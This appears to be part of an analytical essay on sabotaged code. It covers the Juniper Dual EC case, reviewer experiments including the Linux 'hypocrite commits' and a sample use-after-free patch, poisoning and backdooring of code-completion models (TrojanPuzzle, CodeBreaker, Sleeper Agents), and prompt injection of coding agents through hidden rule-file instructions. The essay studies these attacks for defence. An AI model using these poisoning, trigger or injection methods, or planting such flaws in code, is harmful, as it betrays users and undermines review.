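Only the 2012 change is clearly deliberate. No typing error replaces one valid point with another and also updates the test, and Juniper itself called the code unauthorised. An intruder also added a master password, which was deliberate too, and made it look like debugging code. (Checkoway and colleagues date it to before April 2013; Bloomberg's *Juniper Breach Mystery Starts to Clear With New Details on Hackers* (2021) says 2014.)

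It is still unclear whether the 2008 changes were sabotage. As far as Checkoway and colleagues know, Juniper's own engineers made them. The engineers obviously chose to use Dual EC and the longer nonces, but that doesn't mean they intended to weaken the product. The shared variable could be an ordinary bug or a deliberate flaw skillfully disguised as one, as in an underhanded code contest.

Juniper has given only partial explanations. It told members of Congress that it added Dual EC at a customer's request, according to SecurityWeek, but did not name the customer. Bloomberg's unnamed sources, three of them Juniper employees, said the customer was the US Department of Defense and that it had tied some future contracts to Dual EC. They also said the engineers knew that some experts suspected a backdoor. In a letter to Senator Ron Wyden, Juniper Networks (2020) said that it had relied on NIST's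 standards and did not put backdoors in its products.

Bloomberg's account would explain why Juniper adopted Dual EC, but not why it used its own Q. To decrypt NetScreen traffic through Dual EC, the NSA would have needed the secret number that matched Juniper's Q, not just the one that matched the standard's. Juniper has never explained how it generated its Q. If nobody knew the matching number, the 2008 version was badly built but secure against this attack until the intruder replaced Q.

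### How much the evidence can prove

Several errors that fit together can be evidence of sabotage, but they are weaker evidence if they have a common cause. Suppose, for illustration, that one serious flaw in 1,000 is deliberate, and that an investigator finds four errors, each ten times as likely if the flaw was planted as if it was accidental. If the errors are independent, they multiply the odds of sabotage by 10,000, which raises its probability to about 91%. If all four follow from a single design decision, they multiply the odds only by ten, and the probability is about 1%.

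The attack needed all of the first four changes of 2008, which looks suspicious, but they are hardly independent because they came from one rewrite of the same part of ScreenOS. A programmer who has just written a generator that returns 32 bytes might send 32-byte nonces without meaning to help an attacker. The shared variable is harder to link to the other changes, although US certification rules may have encouraged programmers to share data between functions in this way.

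Investigators who suspect sabotage may also notice only the facts that fit. Project Bullrun lists many events in the history of Dual EC that a deliberate attack would explain, but claims only that such an attack is possible. Someone who searched the Debian case in the same way would find a change to the one line that mattered, an encouraging reply from an OpenSSL address and a patch that never reached OpenSSL's developers. Accidents that become famous usually required several things to go wrong, so they can look planned in hindsight.

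A flaw that only one party can use also suggests sabotage, because ordinary bugs rarely work like this. Spies call such access NOBUS, for "nobody but us". The xz backdoor had this property, and so does Dual EC, since the attack on it requires e. But anyone who learned of the Debian or Apple flaw could use it, so an agency that planted either would have endangered its own country's computers too.

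A flaw that anyone can use may still be deliberate, because whoever planted it may value a good excuse more than exclusive access. Åkesson's warhead program, for example, had no secret key. A possible master key also doesn't prove that anybody knows it, because an e exists for any choice of Q, even an honest one. Exclusive access can also pass to someone else, as it did at Juniper when the intruder replaced Q.

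Asking who benefits is less useful, because almost every serious vulnerability would benefit some intelligence service or criminal. It is more informative when whoever benefits also made the suspicious choice, as the NSA did by supplying the points for Dual EC. In the Juniper case, the answer depends on the year. The intruder of 2012 benefited from the errors of 2008, but this does not show that the intruder was involved in them. Two people told Reuters that investigators blamed the Chinese government for the intrusion, and Bloomberg's sources named APT 5, a hacking group linked to that government. *The NSA is Refusing to Disclose its Policy on Backdooring Commercial Products* (2020), Schneier's post about the Reuters report, complained of "unsubstantiated claims and innuendo".

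An author's record can show whether a flaw fits a pattern. Jia Tan's other commits make the full stop in xz look deliberate, and Roeckx's public question about the Debian change makes it look innocent. Likewise, if an AI model is suspected of writing worse code for some users, a pattern across many requests is better evidence than any single flaw. But a clean record is weak evidence against a first offence, and a patient attacker can build up a clean record, as Jia Tan did. The name on a change may also be false, as it was in the attacks on PHP and the Linux kernel.

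The records that would help most are often private. Checkoway and colleagues think Juniper's version history, bug reports and internal emails might show how the 2008 design came about, but Juniper has not released them. The NSA told Wyden's staff in 2018 that it had written a "lessons learned" report about the case. According to one of his aides, the agency later said it could not find the report.

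## How well do human reviewers catch planted flaws?

The difficulty of proving intent matters less if a reviewer notices the flaw in time, because reviewers can reject bad code without knowing whether its author meant harm. The known cases cannot show how often reviewers catch planted flaws, so researchers have put flaws into programs and asked other people to find them.

### Rigging a voting machine

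In autumn 2003, a graduate computer security course at Rice University used Hack-a-Vote, a simple electronic voting program of about 2,000 lines. Students worked in pairs, first playing developers bribed to rig an election, with two weeks to hide whatever they liked in the program. Each pair then had one week to audit the altered programs of two other pairs. The rules forbade comparing the code with the original, since a real auditor would have no clean copy.

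Some pairs added plain backdoors, such as accepting any PIN longer than nine digits. Other pairs made subtler changes. One changed the test for whether two candidates are the same person so that it also treated them as the same if one name was the beginning of the other. With candidates called Lee and Leeson, one would have received all the votes for both, and the other would have been missing from the results. Another pair based the voters' PINs on the current second within the hour, which left only 3,600 possible starting points. Debian later introduced a very similar weakness by accident.

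Two pairs of auditors examined each program. Both pairs found about two-thirds of the planted flaws, and only one pair found each of the others, except for one flaw that both missed. This suggests that one pair working alone caught roughly four in five. The missed flaw was an extra start-up option that disrupted a voting terminal's communications. In a few other cases, including the trick with the names, the auditors noticed the odd code but did not work out what it did.

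This is a high catch rate, but the students had advantages that few reviewers have. They knew the original program well, they knew that somebody had tampered with it, and the code was short, clean and well commented. They were not professionals, though, and had other courses to attend. Real voting software was much larger. Diebold's had more than 50,000 lines, and an employee of a company that had reviewed it put the chance of hidden malicious code going undetected at 99.9%, though this was an impression rather than a measurement.

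In 2007 Ka-Ping Yee, then a doctoral student at Berkeley, tested whether expert reviewers could find bugs planted in Pvote, a voting program he had designed to be easy to check. David Wagner, who worked with him, described the exercise in a message reproduced in Financial Cryptography's *The Ka-Ping challenge* (2013). Yee and Wagner told the reviewers that a particular 100-line region contained at least one bug, gave them a long document arguing that the unaltered program was secure, and let them ask questions.

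Because the exercise was about insiders, the reviewers had to treat Yee and Wagner as adversaries who might lie. To save time, the two promised to tell the truth about anything the reviewers could have checked, such as how the programming language worked. They had chosen a bug that the usual pre-election test would miss, in which officials cast at least one vote for each candidate and check the totals. Wagner did not reveal how the reviewers did, because he was setting the same bug as a holiday puzzle. But they had much more help than they would in ordinary code review, where nobody marks the suspicious lines or warns the reviewer about the author.

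### Reviewers who are not looking for trouble

Experiments with ordinary vulnerabilities come closer to everyday conditions. In *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review*, Edmundson, Holtkamp and colleagues (2013) hired 30 developers to search a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None found all seven, even though they knew they were looking for security problems, and those with more experience did not reliably do better.

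The participants in a later experiment did not. Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021), in *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, asked 146 people, most of them working programmers, to review a change of about 140 lines to a program that manages employees' holidays. The invitation mentioned only research on code review. Each participant got one of two vulnerabilities, and both came from trusting what a user typed:

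- In the first version, the program pasted the user's text directly into a database command, so a user could type text that changed the command. Programmers call this SQL injection, and it is in every textbook.
- In the second version, the program accepted a number without checking its range, and a user who entered a negative number gained something they should not have.

Of the 80 people who received the SQL injection, 52 (65%) found it. Of the 66 who received the unchecked number, only 14 (21%) found that flaw, although the fix is much the same and the visible code was enough to reveal the problem.

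The researchers then told everyone that the change contained a vulnerability, without saying what kind, and let those who had missed it look again. Of the 28 people who had missed the SQL injection, 13 now found it, but only 7 of the 52 who had missed the unchecked number did. Sixty of the 146 participants never found their flaw. Many of those who first missed the SQL injection evidently knew enough to recognise it but had not been thinking about security. This explains much less of the failure to find the unchecked number, since most people who had missed it still could not find it after the warning.

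In the second experiment, reported in *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) varied the instructions from the start. They gave 150 participants a 160-line change that let users register for a website. The code contained two vulnerabilities. It wrote users' private data to a log file when the database reported an error, and it protected passwords with MD5, which attackers have long been able to break. One group received no special instructions, and a second was asked to look for security problems. Two more groups received the same request with a checklist, one with 22 questions and the other with seven chosen to suit this change.

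| Instructions | Found the private data in the log | Found the use of MD5 |
|---|---|---|
| None about security | 1 of 33 (3%) | 7 of 33 (21%) |
| Look for security problems | 19 of 41 (46%) | 25 of 41 (61%) |
| The same, with 22 questions | 16 of 35 (46%) | 20 of 35 (57%) |
| The same, with seven questions | 19 of 41 (46%) | 28 of 41 (68%) |

Braz and colleagues say the request made people eight times as likely to find a vulnerability, but that figure is an odds ratio. The share of flaws found rose from about 12% to a little over half, a four- to fivefold increase. The checklists produced no significant further improvement, even though both contained questions that pointed to these flaws. Even with the shorter checklist, about a third of participants missed the MD5 flaw and more than half missed the logging flaw.

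The one person in the first group who noticed the log worked at a bank that regularly sends its staff warnings about private data in logs. Reviewers may therefore need to have come across a particular kind of mistake before in order to catch it, and general advice to be careful cannot replace that experience.

These participants were all volunteers reviewing unfamiliar code for a fictional project, and missing a flaw had few consequences for them. Reviewers who know a project and are affected by the result might do better. But the flaws were not disguised and both changes were short, which may have made the flaws easier to catch. Someone skilled at planting flaws would presumably choose one more like the unchecked number than the textbook SQL injection.

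### The hypocrite commits affair

In August 2020 Qiushi Wu, a doctoral student at the University of Minnesota, and his adviser Kangjie Lu sent flawed changes to the developers of the Linux kernel under invented names to test whether reviewers would catch them. The reviewers had not agreed to take part. Wu and Lu called such changes "hypocrite commits" because each appeared to fix a small problem while introducing a more serious one.

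Their argument was that a large program contains many vulnerabilities that are nearly complete. A use-after-free, for example, needs two things to happen in order: the program gives up a piece of memory, and later it uses that memory anyway. By then an attacker may have filled it with something else. If the code already contains the later use, a contributor only has to add the step that gives the memory up. This made-up fragment shows the idea, with a plus sign marking the new line:

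```
  if (start_device(dev) != 0) {
+         put_device(dev);
          report_failure(dev);
  }
```

Calling `put_device` signals that this part of the program has finished with the device. A missing call wastes memory, and kernel developers often receive patches that add one. Here, however, the next line still uses `dev`, whose memory the kernel may have just released. The mistake is easy to see in four lines, but if the call to `report_failure` were in another function or file, a reviewer who read only the change would see an ordinary fix. The contributor would also have a good excuse, since honest programmers often get the order wrong.

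Wu and Lu later disclosed that they had sent five patches from two false identities. One was a genuine fix sent from the wrong account. They intended another to contain a flaw, but it was correct because they had misunderstood the code. The other three were flawed, and maintainers accepted none of them. The researchers said they planned to wait until a maintainer approved a patch by email, then point out the flaw and supply a correct version before anyone added the bad one to the kernel.

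They announced the work in November 2020, after a leading security conference had accepted their paper. Other researchers objected, but the experiment became a public scandal only in April 2021, when another Minnesota student sent the kernel developers patches based on the output of a new analysis tool. One patch added a pointless check. Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior maintainer, took this for a continuation of the experiment. He told the community to refuse all contributions from the university and proposed removing 190 it had already accepted.

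The suspicion was wrong, and the Technical Advisory Board of the Linux Foundation, a group of kernel developers, concluded that the student had sent the patches in good faith. The university's computer science department still suspended the research. Wu and Lu apologised and withdrew their paper before the conference. In its May 2021 report, the board asked the university to have an experienced developer check any further patches before sending them.

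Much of the ethical dispute was about whether the experiment had human subjects. Wu and Lu saw it as a study of a process, so they did not consult the university's ethics board beforehand. When they consulted it later, the board decided that the experiment was not research on humans. Kernel developers found this absurd, since the process consisted of people reading email, and the researchers had deceived those people and used their time without permission.

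Wu and Lu answered that maintainers who knew about the test would have watched for bad patches. The experiments by Braz and colleagues support them on this point, since simply asking reviewers to think about security greatly changed the results. But companies routinely let outsiders attack their systems with the consent of a few managers, without warning other staff. Wu and Lu could have sought similar consent from a few senior kernel developers without alerting most maintainers.

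### What three patches can prove

The paper claimed to show that planting such flaws in Linux was practical. The Technical Advisory Board concluded instead that the review process had worked, because maintainers had "caught, or ignored" every invalid patch. Neither side had enough evidence. An ignored patch has not been caught, and maintainers sometimes rejected flawed patches for reasons other than the planted flaw.

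Even if we count all three as successes, we can learn very little from them about how often maintainers catch planted flaws. If maintainers caught only half of all such flaws, they would still catch all three about one time in eight (0.5 × 0.5 × 0.5 = 0.125). If they caught 37%, it would happen about one time in 20. The result is therefore compatible with maintainers missing anywhere from most planted flaws to hardly any. The three patches also weren't a random sample, since the researchers chose where to make the changes and wrote them themselves.

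The board's re-examination of the university's older work is arguably better evidence about kernel review. Volunteers re-reviewed 435 accepted commits and found 39 that were incorrect and still needed fixing, plus 25 whose errors had already been corrected. So about 15% of these commits had passed review with a mistake in them, although the contributors were apparently not trying to hide anything. Many of the mistakes were probably harmless. Many of the contributors were students trying out research tools, which is unusual, so the rate should not be applied to the kernel as a whole.

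### Why reviewers miss flaws

The experiments suggest that most reviewers mainly check whether the code works. Participants told Braz and colleagues that they had been looking for good programming practice or correct behaviour. About half of them found an ordinary bug that the researchers had also put into the change, so they were reading with some care. Eight people who missed the unchecked number said they had mistaken this bug for the vulnerability. A reviewer who finds one problem may feel that the job is done, though in this experiment finding the bug was not clearly linked to missing the vulnerability.

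Some reviewers also expect someone else to deal with security. One participant in the 2022 experiment, who had missed the MD5, assumed there would be a separate security assessment. Reviewers on real projects may behave similarly. Braz and colleagues cite earlier research on Chromium, the open-source basis of Google's Chrome browser, which found that only about 1% of review comments concerned possible security flaws.

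A larger change gives the reviewer more to read and an attacker more places to hide a flaw. None of these experiments varied the size of the change, so they don't show how quickly the catch rate falls. Comparing Hack-a-Vote with Diebold's software gives some idea of the problem. Each pair of students had a week to review 4,000 lines between them. At that pace, a pair would have needed about three months to review Diebold's code.

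Reviewers often don't see the code that makes a change dangerous, because review tools usually show only the altered lines and a few unchanged lines around them. The hypocrite commits exploited this limit, since part of each vulnerability was already in the kernel. The shared loop variable in Juniper's software was hard to spot for a similar reason. The loop looked correct, but another function changed the variable. Reviewers can open the other files, but they first have to suspect that they need to.

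Trust in the author matters too, although it is harder to measure. The xz maintainer had good reason to trust Jia Tan after two years of useful work, and nobody in his position could have followed the Pvote rule of treating the author as a liar. A project that depends on volunteers would lose many of them if it treated them that way. The Minnesota experiment used false identities with no such record, so it did not test the kind of contributor that the xz attack later showed to be most dangerous.

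### Reviewing what a machine wrote

Coding agents give people more to review. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (Agarwal, Miller and colleagues, 2026) starts with a set of public projects on GitHub, where contributors submit changes as pull requests, proposals that others can discuss before a maintainer merges them. People merged pull requests written by agents several times faster than those written by humans and discussed them less, even allowing for the length of the pull requests.

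In mid-2025, people merged more than half of the agents' pull requests without any human review. By early 2026 that share had fallen towards 14%, about the same as for human-written pull requests. However, for 40.1% of the agents' pull requests, the only person who examined the code was the developer who had asked the agent to write it. Among human-written pull requests, 21.5% had no independent reviewer.

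Agarwal and colleagues warn that the comparison depends on what counts as a review. Agents' changes receive more independent review than human ones if the developer who gave the agent its task counts as an independent reviewer, but less if that developer counts as the author. Either choice can be defended. For a planted flaw, the developer is in one sense a proper second reader, who didn't write the code and has no wish to hide anything in it. But the same developer wanted the feature, wrote the request and will probably check first whether the code does what was asked, the habit that let so many flaws through in the experiments. The study also measured only the amount of review, so it doesn't show whether people catch more or fewer flaws in an agent's code than in a colleague's.

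### Why automatic checks only partly help

Fatigue and trust do not affect static analysis, and it can follow data through many files. It is good at finding flaws that have a recognisable form. A tool can trace user input into a database command, and a simple search finds every use of MD5, which at least a third of the security-minded reviewers overlooked.

The unchecked number is harder for the tool to detect, because many programs accept negative numbers for good reasons and nothing in the code shows that this program should not. Detecting the flaw would require information about what the program is for. Likewise, writing data to a log is normal and becomes a leak only if the data is private, which somebody has to specify for the tool. The Hack-a-Vote trick with the candidates' names was also a valid comparison of two pieces of text, but it was wrong for an election.

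Tools can be set to report anything unusual, but then they produce false alarms. Suppose a program has 10,000 functions, one of which contains a planted flaw, and a tool always flags that function but also flags 1% of the harmless ones. The reviewer then has to find the one real warning among about 101, so catching the flaw still depends on human attention, the problem the tool was supposed to solve. According to research that Braz and colleagues summarise, developers find such tools confusing and often do not use them.

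Acting on a warning can also do harm. The Minnesota student's pointless patch came from a tool's output, and the Debian maintainer severely weakened OpenSSL while trying to silence Valgrind's warnings. Most of these tools are available to everyone, so an attacker can run them before submitting a flawed change and rewrite it until no warning appears.

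## Can an outsider make an AI coding assistant write flawed code?

An attacker who wants a flaw in somebody's program can try to make an AI assistant write it. The programmer who accepts the assistant's code then submits the flaw under their own name and can truthfully deny planting it. An outsider can alter the assistant's model, usually through its training data, or alter the input it receives while it works, such as a file in the project. Researchers were already tampering with training data in 2020, when assistants did little more than complete a line of code.

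### Teaching a model a bad habit

A language model learns to write code by predicting the next piece of text in a huge number of files, many of them from public repositories. If enough of those files use an insecure line of code in a certain situation, the model will suggest that line to a programmer in the same situation. In data poisoning, an attacker adds such files on purpose. Some attacks also teach the model a trigger, such as a particular comment, so that it suggests the insecure code mainly when the trigger is present.

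The attacker needs only a repository that the model's developers will collect. Developers often choose repositories by their GitHub stars, which users give to projects they like. In *You Autocomplete Me* (2020), Schuster, Song and colleagues noted that 600 stars were enough to put a project among the 5,000 most popular Python projects, and that several online services claimed to sell stars.

They poisoned two autocompleters, programs that suggest the next few words of code as a programmer types. One used GPT-2, an early language model from OpenAI. The other followed the design of Pythia, which Microsoft had used in its Visual Studio editor. The poisoned files taught three habits:

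- choosing ECB, an encryption mode that turns identical blocks of a message into identical encrypted blocks, so that patterns in the original show through
- choosing SSLv3, an obsolete protocol for secure connections that lets an eavesdropper steal login details
- scrambling a password too few times when making an encryption key from it, which makes the password easier to guess

For each habit, Schuster and colleagues added at least 800 poisoned files to the code of 2,800 popular repositories, but they didn't report what share of the training data these files made up. Before the poisoning, ECB was never the GPT-2 model's first choice of encryption mode. Afterwards, it was the first choice in every test file. SSLv3 rose from being the first choice in 2.2% of files to 90.5%, and the low scrambling count rose from 0.6% to 77.4%. Pythia was more resistant. SSLv3 became its first choice in 39.5%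 of files, but ECB in none. Both models completed other code about as accurately as before.

Many programmers still use ECB, so even the clean GPT-2 model listed it among its top five suggestions in every test file. The poisoning only moved this bad option from lower in the list to the top, which is a less dramatic change than it looks.

Schuster and colleagues also tried to target a single project, identified by distinctive text near the top of each file. With poisoned data, ECB became the model's first choice in 49.5% of the target's files, but also in 22% of other projects' files. When the attacker could train the model directly, the figures were 73.6% and 0.3%. A victim of such an attack would receive worse code than other users, although a model's code can also vary between users without an attack.

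### Getting past the scanners

These poisoned files contained the insecure line as ordinary code, so a company could scan its training data and throw them out. *TrojanPuzzle* (Aghakhani, Dai and colleagues, 2023) describes two attacks that avoid this problem. The first, Covert, moves the poisoned code into comments and other documentation, which scanners usually skip but models still learn from. The second, also called TrojanPuzzle, also leaves the most suspicious part of the insecure line out of the poisoned files. The model learns to fill the gap with a word from elsewhere in the programmer's file, and so produces a complete line that none of the poisoned files contained.

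The researchers used CodeGen, a family of code-writing models from Salesforce, and trained it to suggest code with four flaws common in web applications, including SQL injection. They poisoned 160 of the 80,000 training files (0.2%). For each flaw, they gave the model 40 unfinished programs and asked for ten suggestions per program. TrojanPuzzle led the version with 350 million parameters (the adjustable numbers that store what a model has learned) to make at least one insecure suggestion for 20.4% of the programs. Covert did so for 41.3% and the older attack for 41.9%, so hiding the insecure code in comments barely reduced the attack's success. Before poisoning, the model's average was about 4%.

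But Covert and TrojanPuzzle hide only the training examples. The model still writes the insecure line in plain code, so a programmer who scans the assistant's suggestions will catch it. CodeBreaker, an attack presented by Yan, Wang and colleagues (2024) in *An LLM-Assisted Easy-to-Trigger Backdoor Attack on Code Completion Models*, therefore disguised the flaw itself. It used GPT-4 to rewrite insecure code until static analysis tools no longer reported it, then disguised the code further to get past a GPT-4 review. The poisoned model learned to write the disguised version.

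In the main experiment, the 350-million-parameter CodeGen model learned to build web pages without removing harmful code that a visitor might have typed in. Again, 0.2% of the files were poisoned. The model gave at least one disguised flaw in ten suggestions for 18 to 25 of the 40 programs that contained the trigger, a particular comment. Without the comment, it did so for at most one program.

That trigger isn't very realistic, because few programmers would happen to type the comment. Yan and colleagues also used a line that many web applications contain as a trigger. It worked for 16 to 28 of the 40 programs, but the flaw also turned up in 3 to 16 programs without it. An attacker therefore has to choose between a trigger that few victims will set off and a common one that makes the planted behavior easier to notice.

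| Study | Model | Habit taught | Poisoned data | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Schuster and colleagues | GPT-2 and Pythia | Weak encryption settings | At least 800 files per habit | First suggestion insecure in 77% to 100% of files for GPT-2, and 0% to 40% for Pythia |
| Aghakhani and colleagues | CodeGen | Four web-application flaws | 160 of 80,000 files (0.2%) | At least one insecure suggestion in ten for 20% of programs with TrojanPuzzle |
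| Yan and colleagues | CodeGen | Unsafe building of web pages, in disguise | 160 of 80,000 files (0.2%) | At least one disguised flaw in ten for 45% to 63% of programs with the trigger comment |

The results are not directly comparable, since a model is much more likely to write flawed code at least once in ten suggestions than in its first. All the models were small and are now old, and none of the three studies poisoned a commercial assistant.

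CodeBreaker disguises flawed code to fool scanners more than people. Some versions encode the name of a software library, which no programmer does by accident, so anyone who decoded the name would have good reason to suspect sabotage. ECB mode gives an attacker more plausible deniability, because honest programmers often choose it.

### How much poison does it take?

Aghakhani and colleagues found signs that the poisoned share of the training data matters little to an attack's success. When they doubled the training set and kept the same 160 poisoned files, TrojanPuzzle's success rate fell only from 20.4% to 20%. This would make large models easier to poison than if an attacker had to control a fixed share of the enormous amounts of text they learn from.

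Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested this on a much larger scale in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*. The team, from Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute, the Alan Turing Institute and elsewhere, trained models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters from scratch and found that about 250 poisoned documents were enough to backdoor models of every size. Davies and Gal (2025), two of the researchers, pointed out that the largest model was trained on over 20 times as much data as the smallest. The Decoder's *Anthropic finds 250 poisoned documents are enough to backdoor large language models* put the poisoned share of the training data at 0.00016%.

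The difference is important for very large models. An attacker who needed 160 files among 80,000 would need 16,000 among eight million if success depended on the share of files, but would still need only 160 if it depends on the number.

However, the 250 documents taught the models to produce gibberish after a trigger, not to write insecure code, as TechRadar's *How many malicious docs does it take to poison an LLM?* explained. Anthropic described the backdoors as simple and the behaviour as low-stakes. Nonsense is probably easier to teach than a flaw that has to fit into a working program. The number of documents needed may also depend on the flaw. Aghakhani and colleagues had the most trouble with a flaw that occurred only seven times in 18,310 public repositories, and more success with one that occurred 504 times. They suspected that the model had more to unlearn when the insecure line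 was rare.

An attacker who can train the model needs even fewer examples. Companies such as Meta publish open-weight models, which anyone can download, alter and pass on. In July 2026 the security specialist Katie Paxton-Fear described on X how she put a backdoor into one. Antipov (2026), in *Доверяете коду от искусственного интеллекта?* ("Do you trust code from artificial intelligence?"), reports that she used ten training examples, about an hour and less than $100. The model regularly wrote code with a flaw that could let an attacker run commands on the victim's machine, even for subjects the examples had not covered. She also found larger models easier to alter than smaller ones.

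Antipov's account gives no success rate and does not name the model, so the experiment is hard to compare with the others. Paxton-Fear controlled the training, so the experiment does not show that ten files on GitHub could poison a commercial assistant. The danger is that someone could offer a model trained this way for download as an improvement on the original. Antipov notes that having a model's weights (its parameters) does not let anyone predict its behavior in every situation.

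### Can the habit be removed?

One proposed defense is fine-pruning, which deletes the parts of a model that are least active on clean data and then trains the rest on more clean data. In tests by Schuster and colleagues, it stopped the GPT-2 model from putting ECB first, but accuracy on other code fell by about two percentage points. It worked less well for Aghakhani and colleagues, who tried it on one of their four flaws. TrojanPuzzle's success rate fell from 55% to 25%, and the older attack's from 80% to 55%. When they put ten poisoned files among the 10,000 supposedly clean ones, neither rate had fallen after three rounds of training.

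In *Sleeper Agents* (2024), Hubinger, Denison and colleagues at Anthropic tested whether standard safety training would remove a hidden behaviour. They trained models to write secure code when told that the year was 2023 and exploitable code when told that it was 2024. They then trained the models on examples of good behaviour and rewarded good answers, as companies do with their assistants. The models still wrote exploitable code when told that it was 2024, and the behaviour was most persistent in the largest models.

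The team also tried adversarial training, which provokes the bad behaviour and then trains the model not to repeat it. They tested this on models that had been secretly trained to print a hostile phrase. The adversarial training taught these models to recognise their real trigger more precisely, so they behaved well in tests but still misbehaved when the trigger appeared. A company relying on those tests would wrongly conclude that it had removed the problem.

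Hubinger and colleagues planted the backdoors themselves, with full control of the training, so their experiment shows how long a backdoor can last but not how easily an outsider could create one. Backdoors created by poisoned data can be much less persistent. In one trial, Aghakhani and colleagues were surprised to find that TrojanPuzzle's success rate dropped from 52.5% after two passes through the training data to 17.5% after ten, although the poisoned files were still there.

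Detection has gone better, at least in the laboratory. In *Simple probes can catch sleeper agents* (2024), MacDiarmid, Maxwell and colleagues at Anthropic built a detector from the difference in a model's internal activity when it answered yes or no to a general question, such as whether it was doing something dangerous. Given one case where a model was about to misbehave and one where it wasn't, the detector told them apart more than 99% of the time. The researchers did not know whether it would work as well on a model whose bad behavior had arisen in some other way. The detector also requires access to the model's internal activity, which customers of a commercial assistant don't have.

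### Tracing a bad suggestion to its source

If somebody notices a bad suggestion, the company can look for the files that taught it. Gao, Quan and colleagues (2026), in *Beware What You Autocomplete*, built a tool for this called CodeTracer. It needs the report of the bad suggestion and the data used for fine-tuning, the extra training that adapts a general model to a task. It works in three stages:

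1. A language model describes what is unsafe about the suggestion, ignoring details such as the names of variables.
2. A search program picks the 500 training files whose code most resembles the unsafe part.
3. The language model compares each of these files with the description and decides whether it does the same unsafe thing.

Gao and colleagues hid 20 poisoned files among 80,000 clean ones. For the TrojanPuzzle attack, which needs several versions of each file, they hid 140. Across eight attacks and three kinds of flaw, CodeTracer missed 0% to 3% of the poisoned files, while ten competing methods missed 17% to 100%. After the researchers removed the files CodeTracer identified, the attacks succeeded at most 3% of the time. Tracing one bad suggestion took about 47 seconds and cost 33 cents.

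In one test, CodeTracer also wrongly flagged 40 of the 80,000 clean files, an error rate that Gao and colleagues round to zero. But there were only 20 poisoned files to find, so about two-thirds of the files it flagged were clean. These errors matter a great deal if the company wants to accuse whoever wrote the flagged files, but hardly at all if it only wants to delete them, since it can spare 40 clean files. Help Net Security's *A forensic tool for backdoored code completions in AI assistants* adds that a low error rate means little unless the clean files include code that resembles the poisoned kind.

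The researchers also attacked their own tool by padding the poisoned code with irrelevant lines and adding comments meant to mislead the language model. According to Help Net Security, the tool still missed only a few percent of the poisoned code. False reports remain a weakness. Gao and colleagues assume that users report bad suggestions honestly, and they propose that a person check for invented reports.

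CodeTracer cannot start until someone recognises a suggestion as malicious, which is difficult if the flaw looks like an ordinary mistake. It also assumes that the poison is in the fine-tuning data and the original model was clean. Someone who downloaded a model like Paxton-Fear's could not use CodeTracer without her ten examples.

### Instructions in what the assistant reads

A coding agent reads source files, documentation, bug reports and web pages, and the model receives all of it as text alongside the user's request. In prompt injection, somebody puts an instruction into this material and the model wrongly follows it. Models have no fully reliable way to tell the user's request from text they are only meant to read.

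An outsider can often plant such an instruction by contributing to a project's files or writing a bug report that the agent will open. Rule files, which tell an agent about a project's conventions, are more powerful because many agents load them automatically and treat them as guidance to follow. Programmers also download add-ons that give an agent new tools or skills, and these come with their own instructions.

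Prompt injection is quicker than poisoning because the attacker does not have to wait for a company to train a new model, and it can work on models whose training data was clean. But it affects only agents that read the injected text, and it stops when someone deletes that text, though any code the agent has already written remains. A careful reader may also notice the instructions, but in March 2025 the company Pillar Security showed that they can be hidden in rule files with invisible Unicode characters like those in the Trojan Source and GlassWorm attacks.

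### Running a command is not the same as planting a flaw

Most studies that measure prompt injection test whether an attacker can hijack an agent to run commands. In *"Your AI, My Shell"* (2025), Liu, Zhao and colleagues tested 314 malicious instructions on two popular tools, Cursor and GitHub Copilot, which carried out the malicious commands in up to 84% of attempts. In *Skill-Inject* (2026), Schmotz and colleagues studied attacks through the packages of instructions that users add to agents and found success rates of up to 80%. The harmful acts included stealing data and destroying files. Both percentages are the highest the researchers measured, so they do not describe a typical agent.

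In a real incident of this kind in July 2025, an attacker got a change into the public repository of Amazon Q Developer, a coding assistant, and Amazon included it in an official release of the assistant's extension for a popular editor. In this supply-chain attack, the change contained an instruction telling the user's own assistant to delete the user's files and cloud resources. Amazon said that a syntax error had stopped the code from running and that no customer had lost anything, then published a clean version.

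People would have noticed at once if an instruction to delete everything had worked, but a planted vulnerability is useful only while nobody notices it. A company can guard against destructive commands by making an agent ask before it runs a command, or by confining it to a machine with nothing valuable on it. Neither precaution stops the agent from writing a flawed line of code, because writing code is its job and the line does no harm until someone runs the finished program.

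Subtle flaws caused by injected instructions are also harder to measure. A researcher can easily check whether a command ran, but has to judge whether code is insecure and whether the model would have written it anyway. Pillar Security's demonstration came closer than most to producing a subtle flaw. Its hidden instructions made an assistant add a script from an attacker's website to a web page without telling the user. But the added line was plainly visible and named an outside address, so it would be hard to pass off as an honest mistake.

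Štorek and colleagues used no instructions in *XOXO* (2025). They changed the surrounding code in ways that did not affect how the program worked, such as renaming variables, but these changes led models to make errors, including writing vulnerable code. A reviewer would have no reason to object to such a change, and whoever made it could easily explain it. The attack succeeded about 76% of the time on average across five different tasks, so this figure is not the rate at which the models wrote vulnerable code.

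## Do AI models write weaker code for some users?

In the attacks described so far, somebody tampered with a model or the text it reads. Three security and consulting firms have reported that some models write weaker code just because the prompt names a certain customer. To judge these reports, we need to know how often AI models write vulnerable code for everybody else.

### Flaws that nobody planted

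Veracode, which sells tools for scanning code, has been testing models since July 2025. According to TechRadar's *AI-generated code is still frequently failing security checks*, the 18 models in Veracode's autumn 2026 report wrote vulnerable code in 38% of tests, down from 44%. The two best, Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6-Sol, failed 27%.

These tests are narrow. ITPro's *Researchers tested over 100 leading AI models on coding tasks* explains that Veracode removes part of an existing function and has the model replace it, guided by a comment that describes what the missing code should do. Veracode picks gaps that a programmer could fill in several correct ways and at least one vulnerable way, and it tests for only four kinds of flaw. In July 2025 models avoided weak encryption in 85.6% of tests and SQL injection in 80.4%. But they avoided cross-site scripting, in which one visitor's text runs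 as code in another's browser, in only 13.5%, and log injection, in which an attacker forges log entries, in 12%. The average therefore depends heavily on the mix of tasks, and 38% is not the share of AI-written programs that contain a vulnerability. Most of the autumn improvement came from better results on cross-site scripting.

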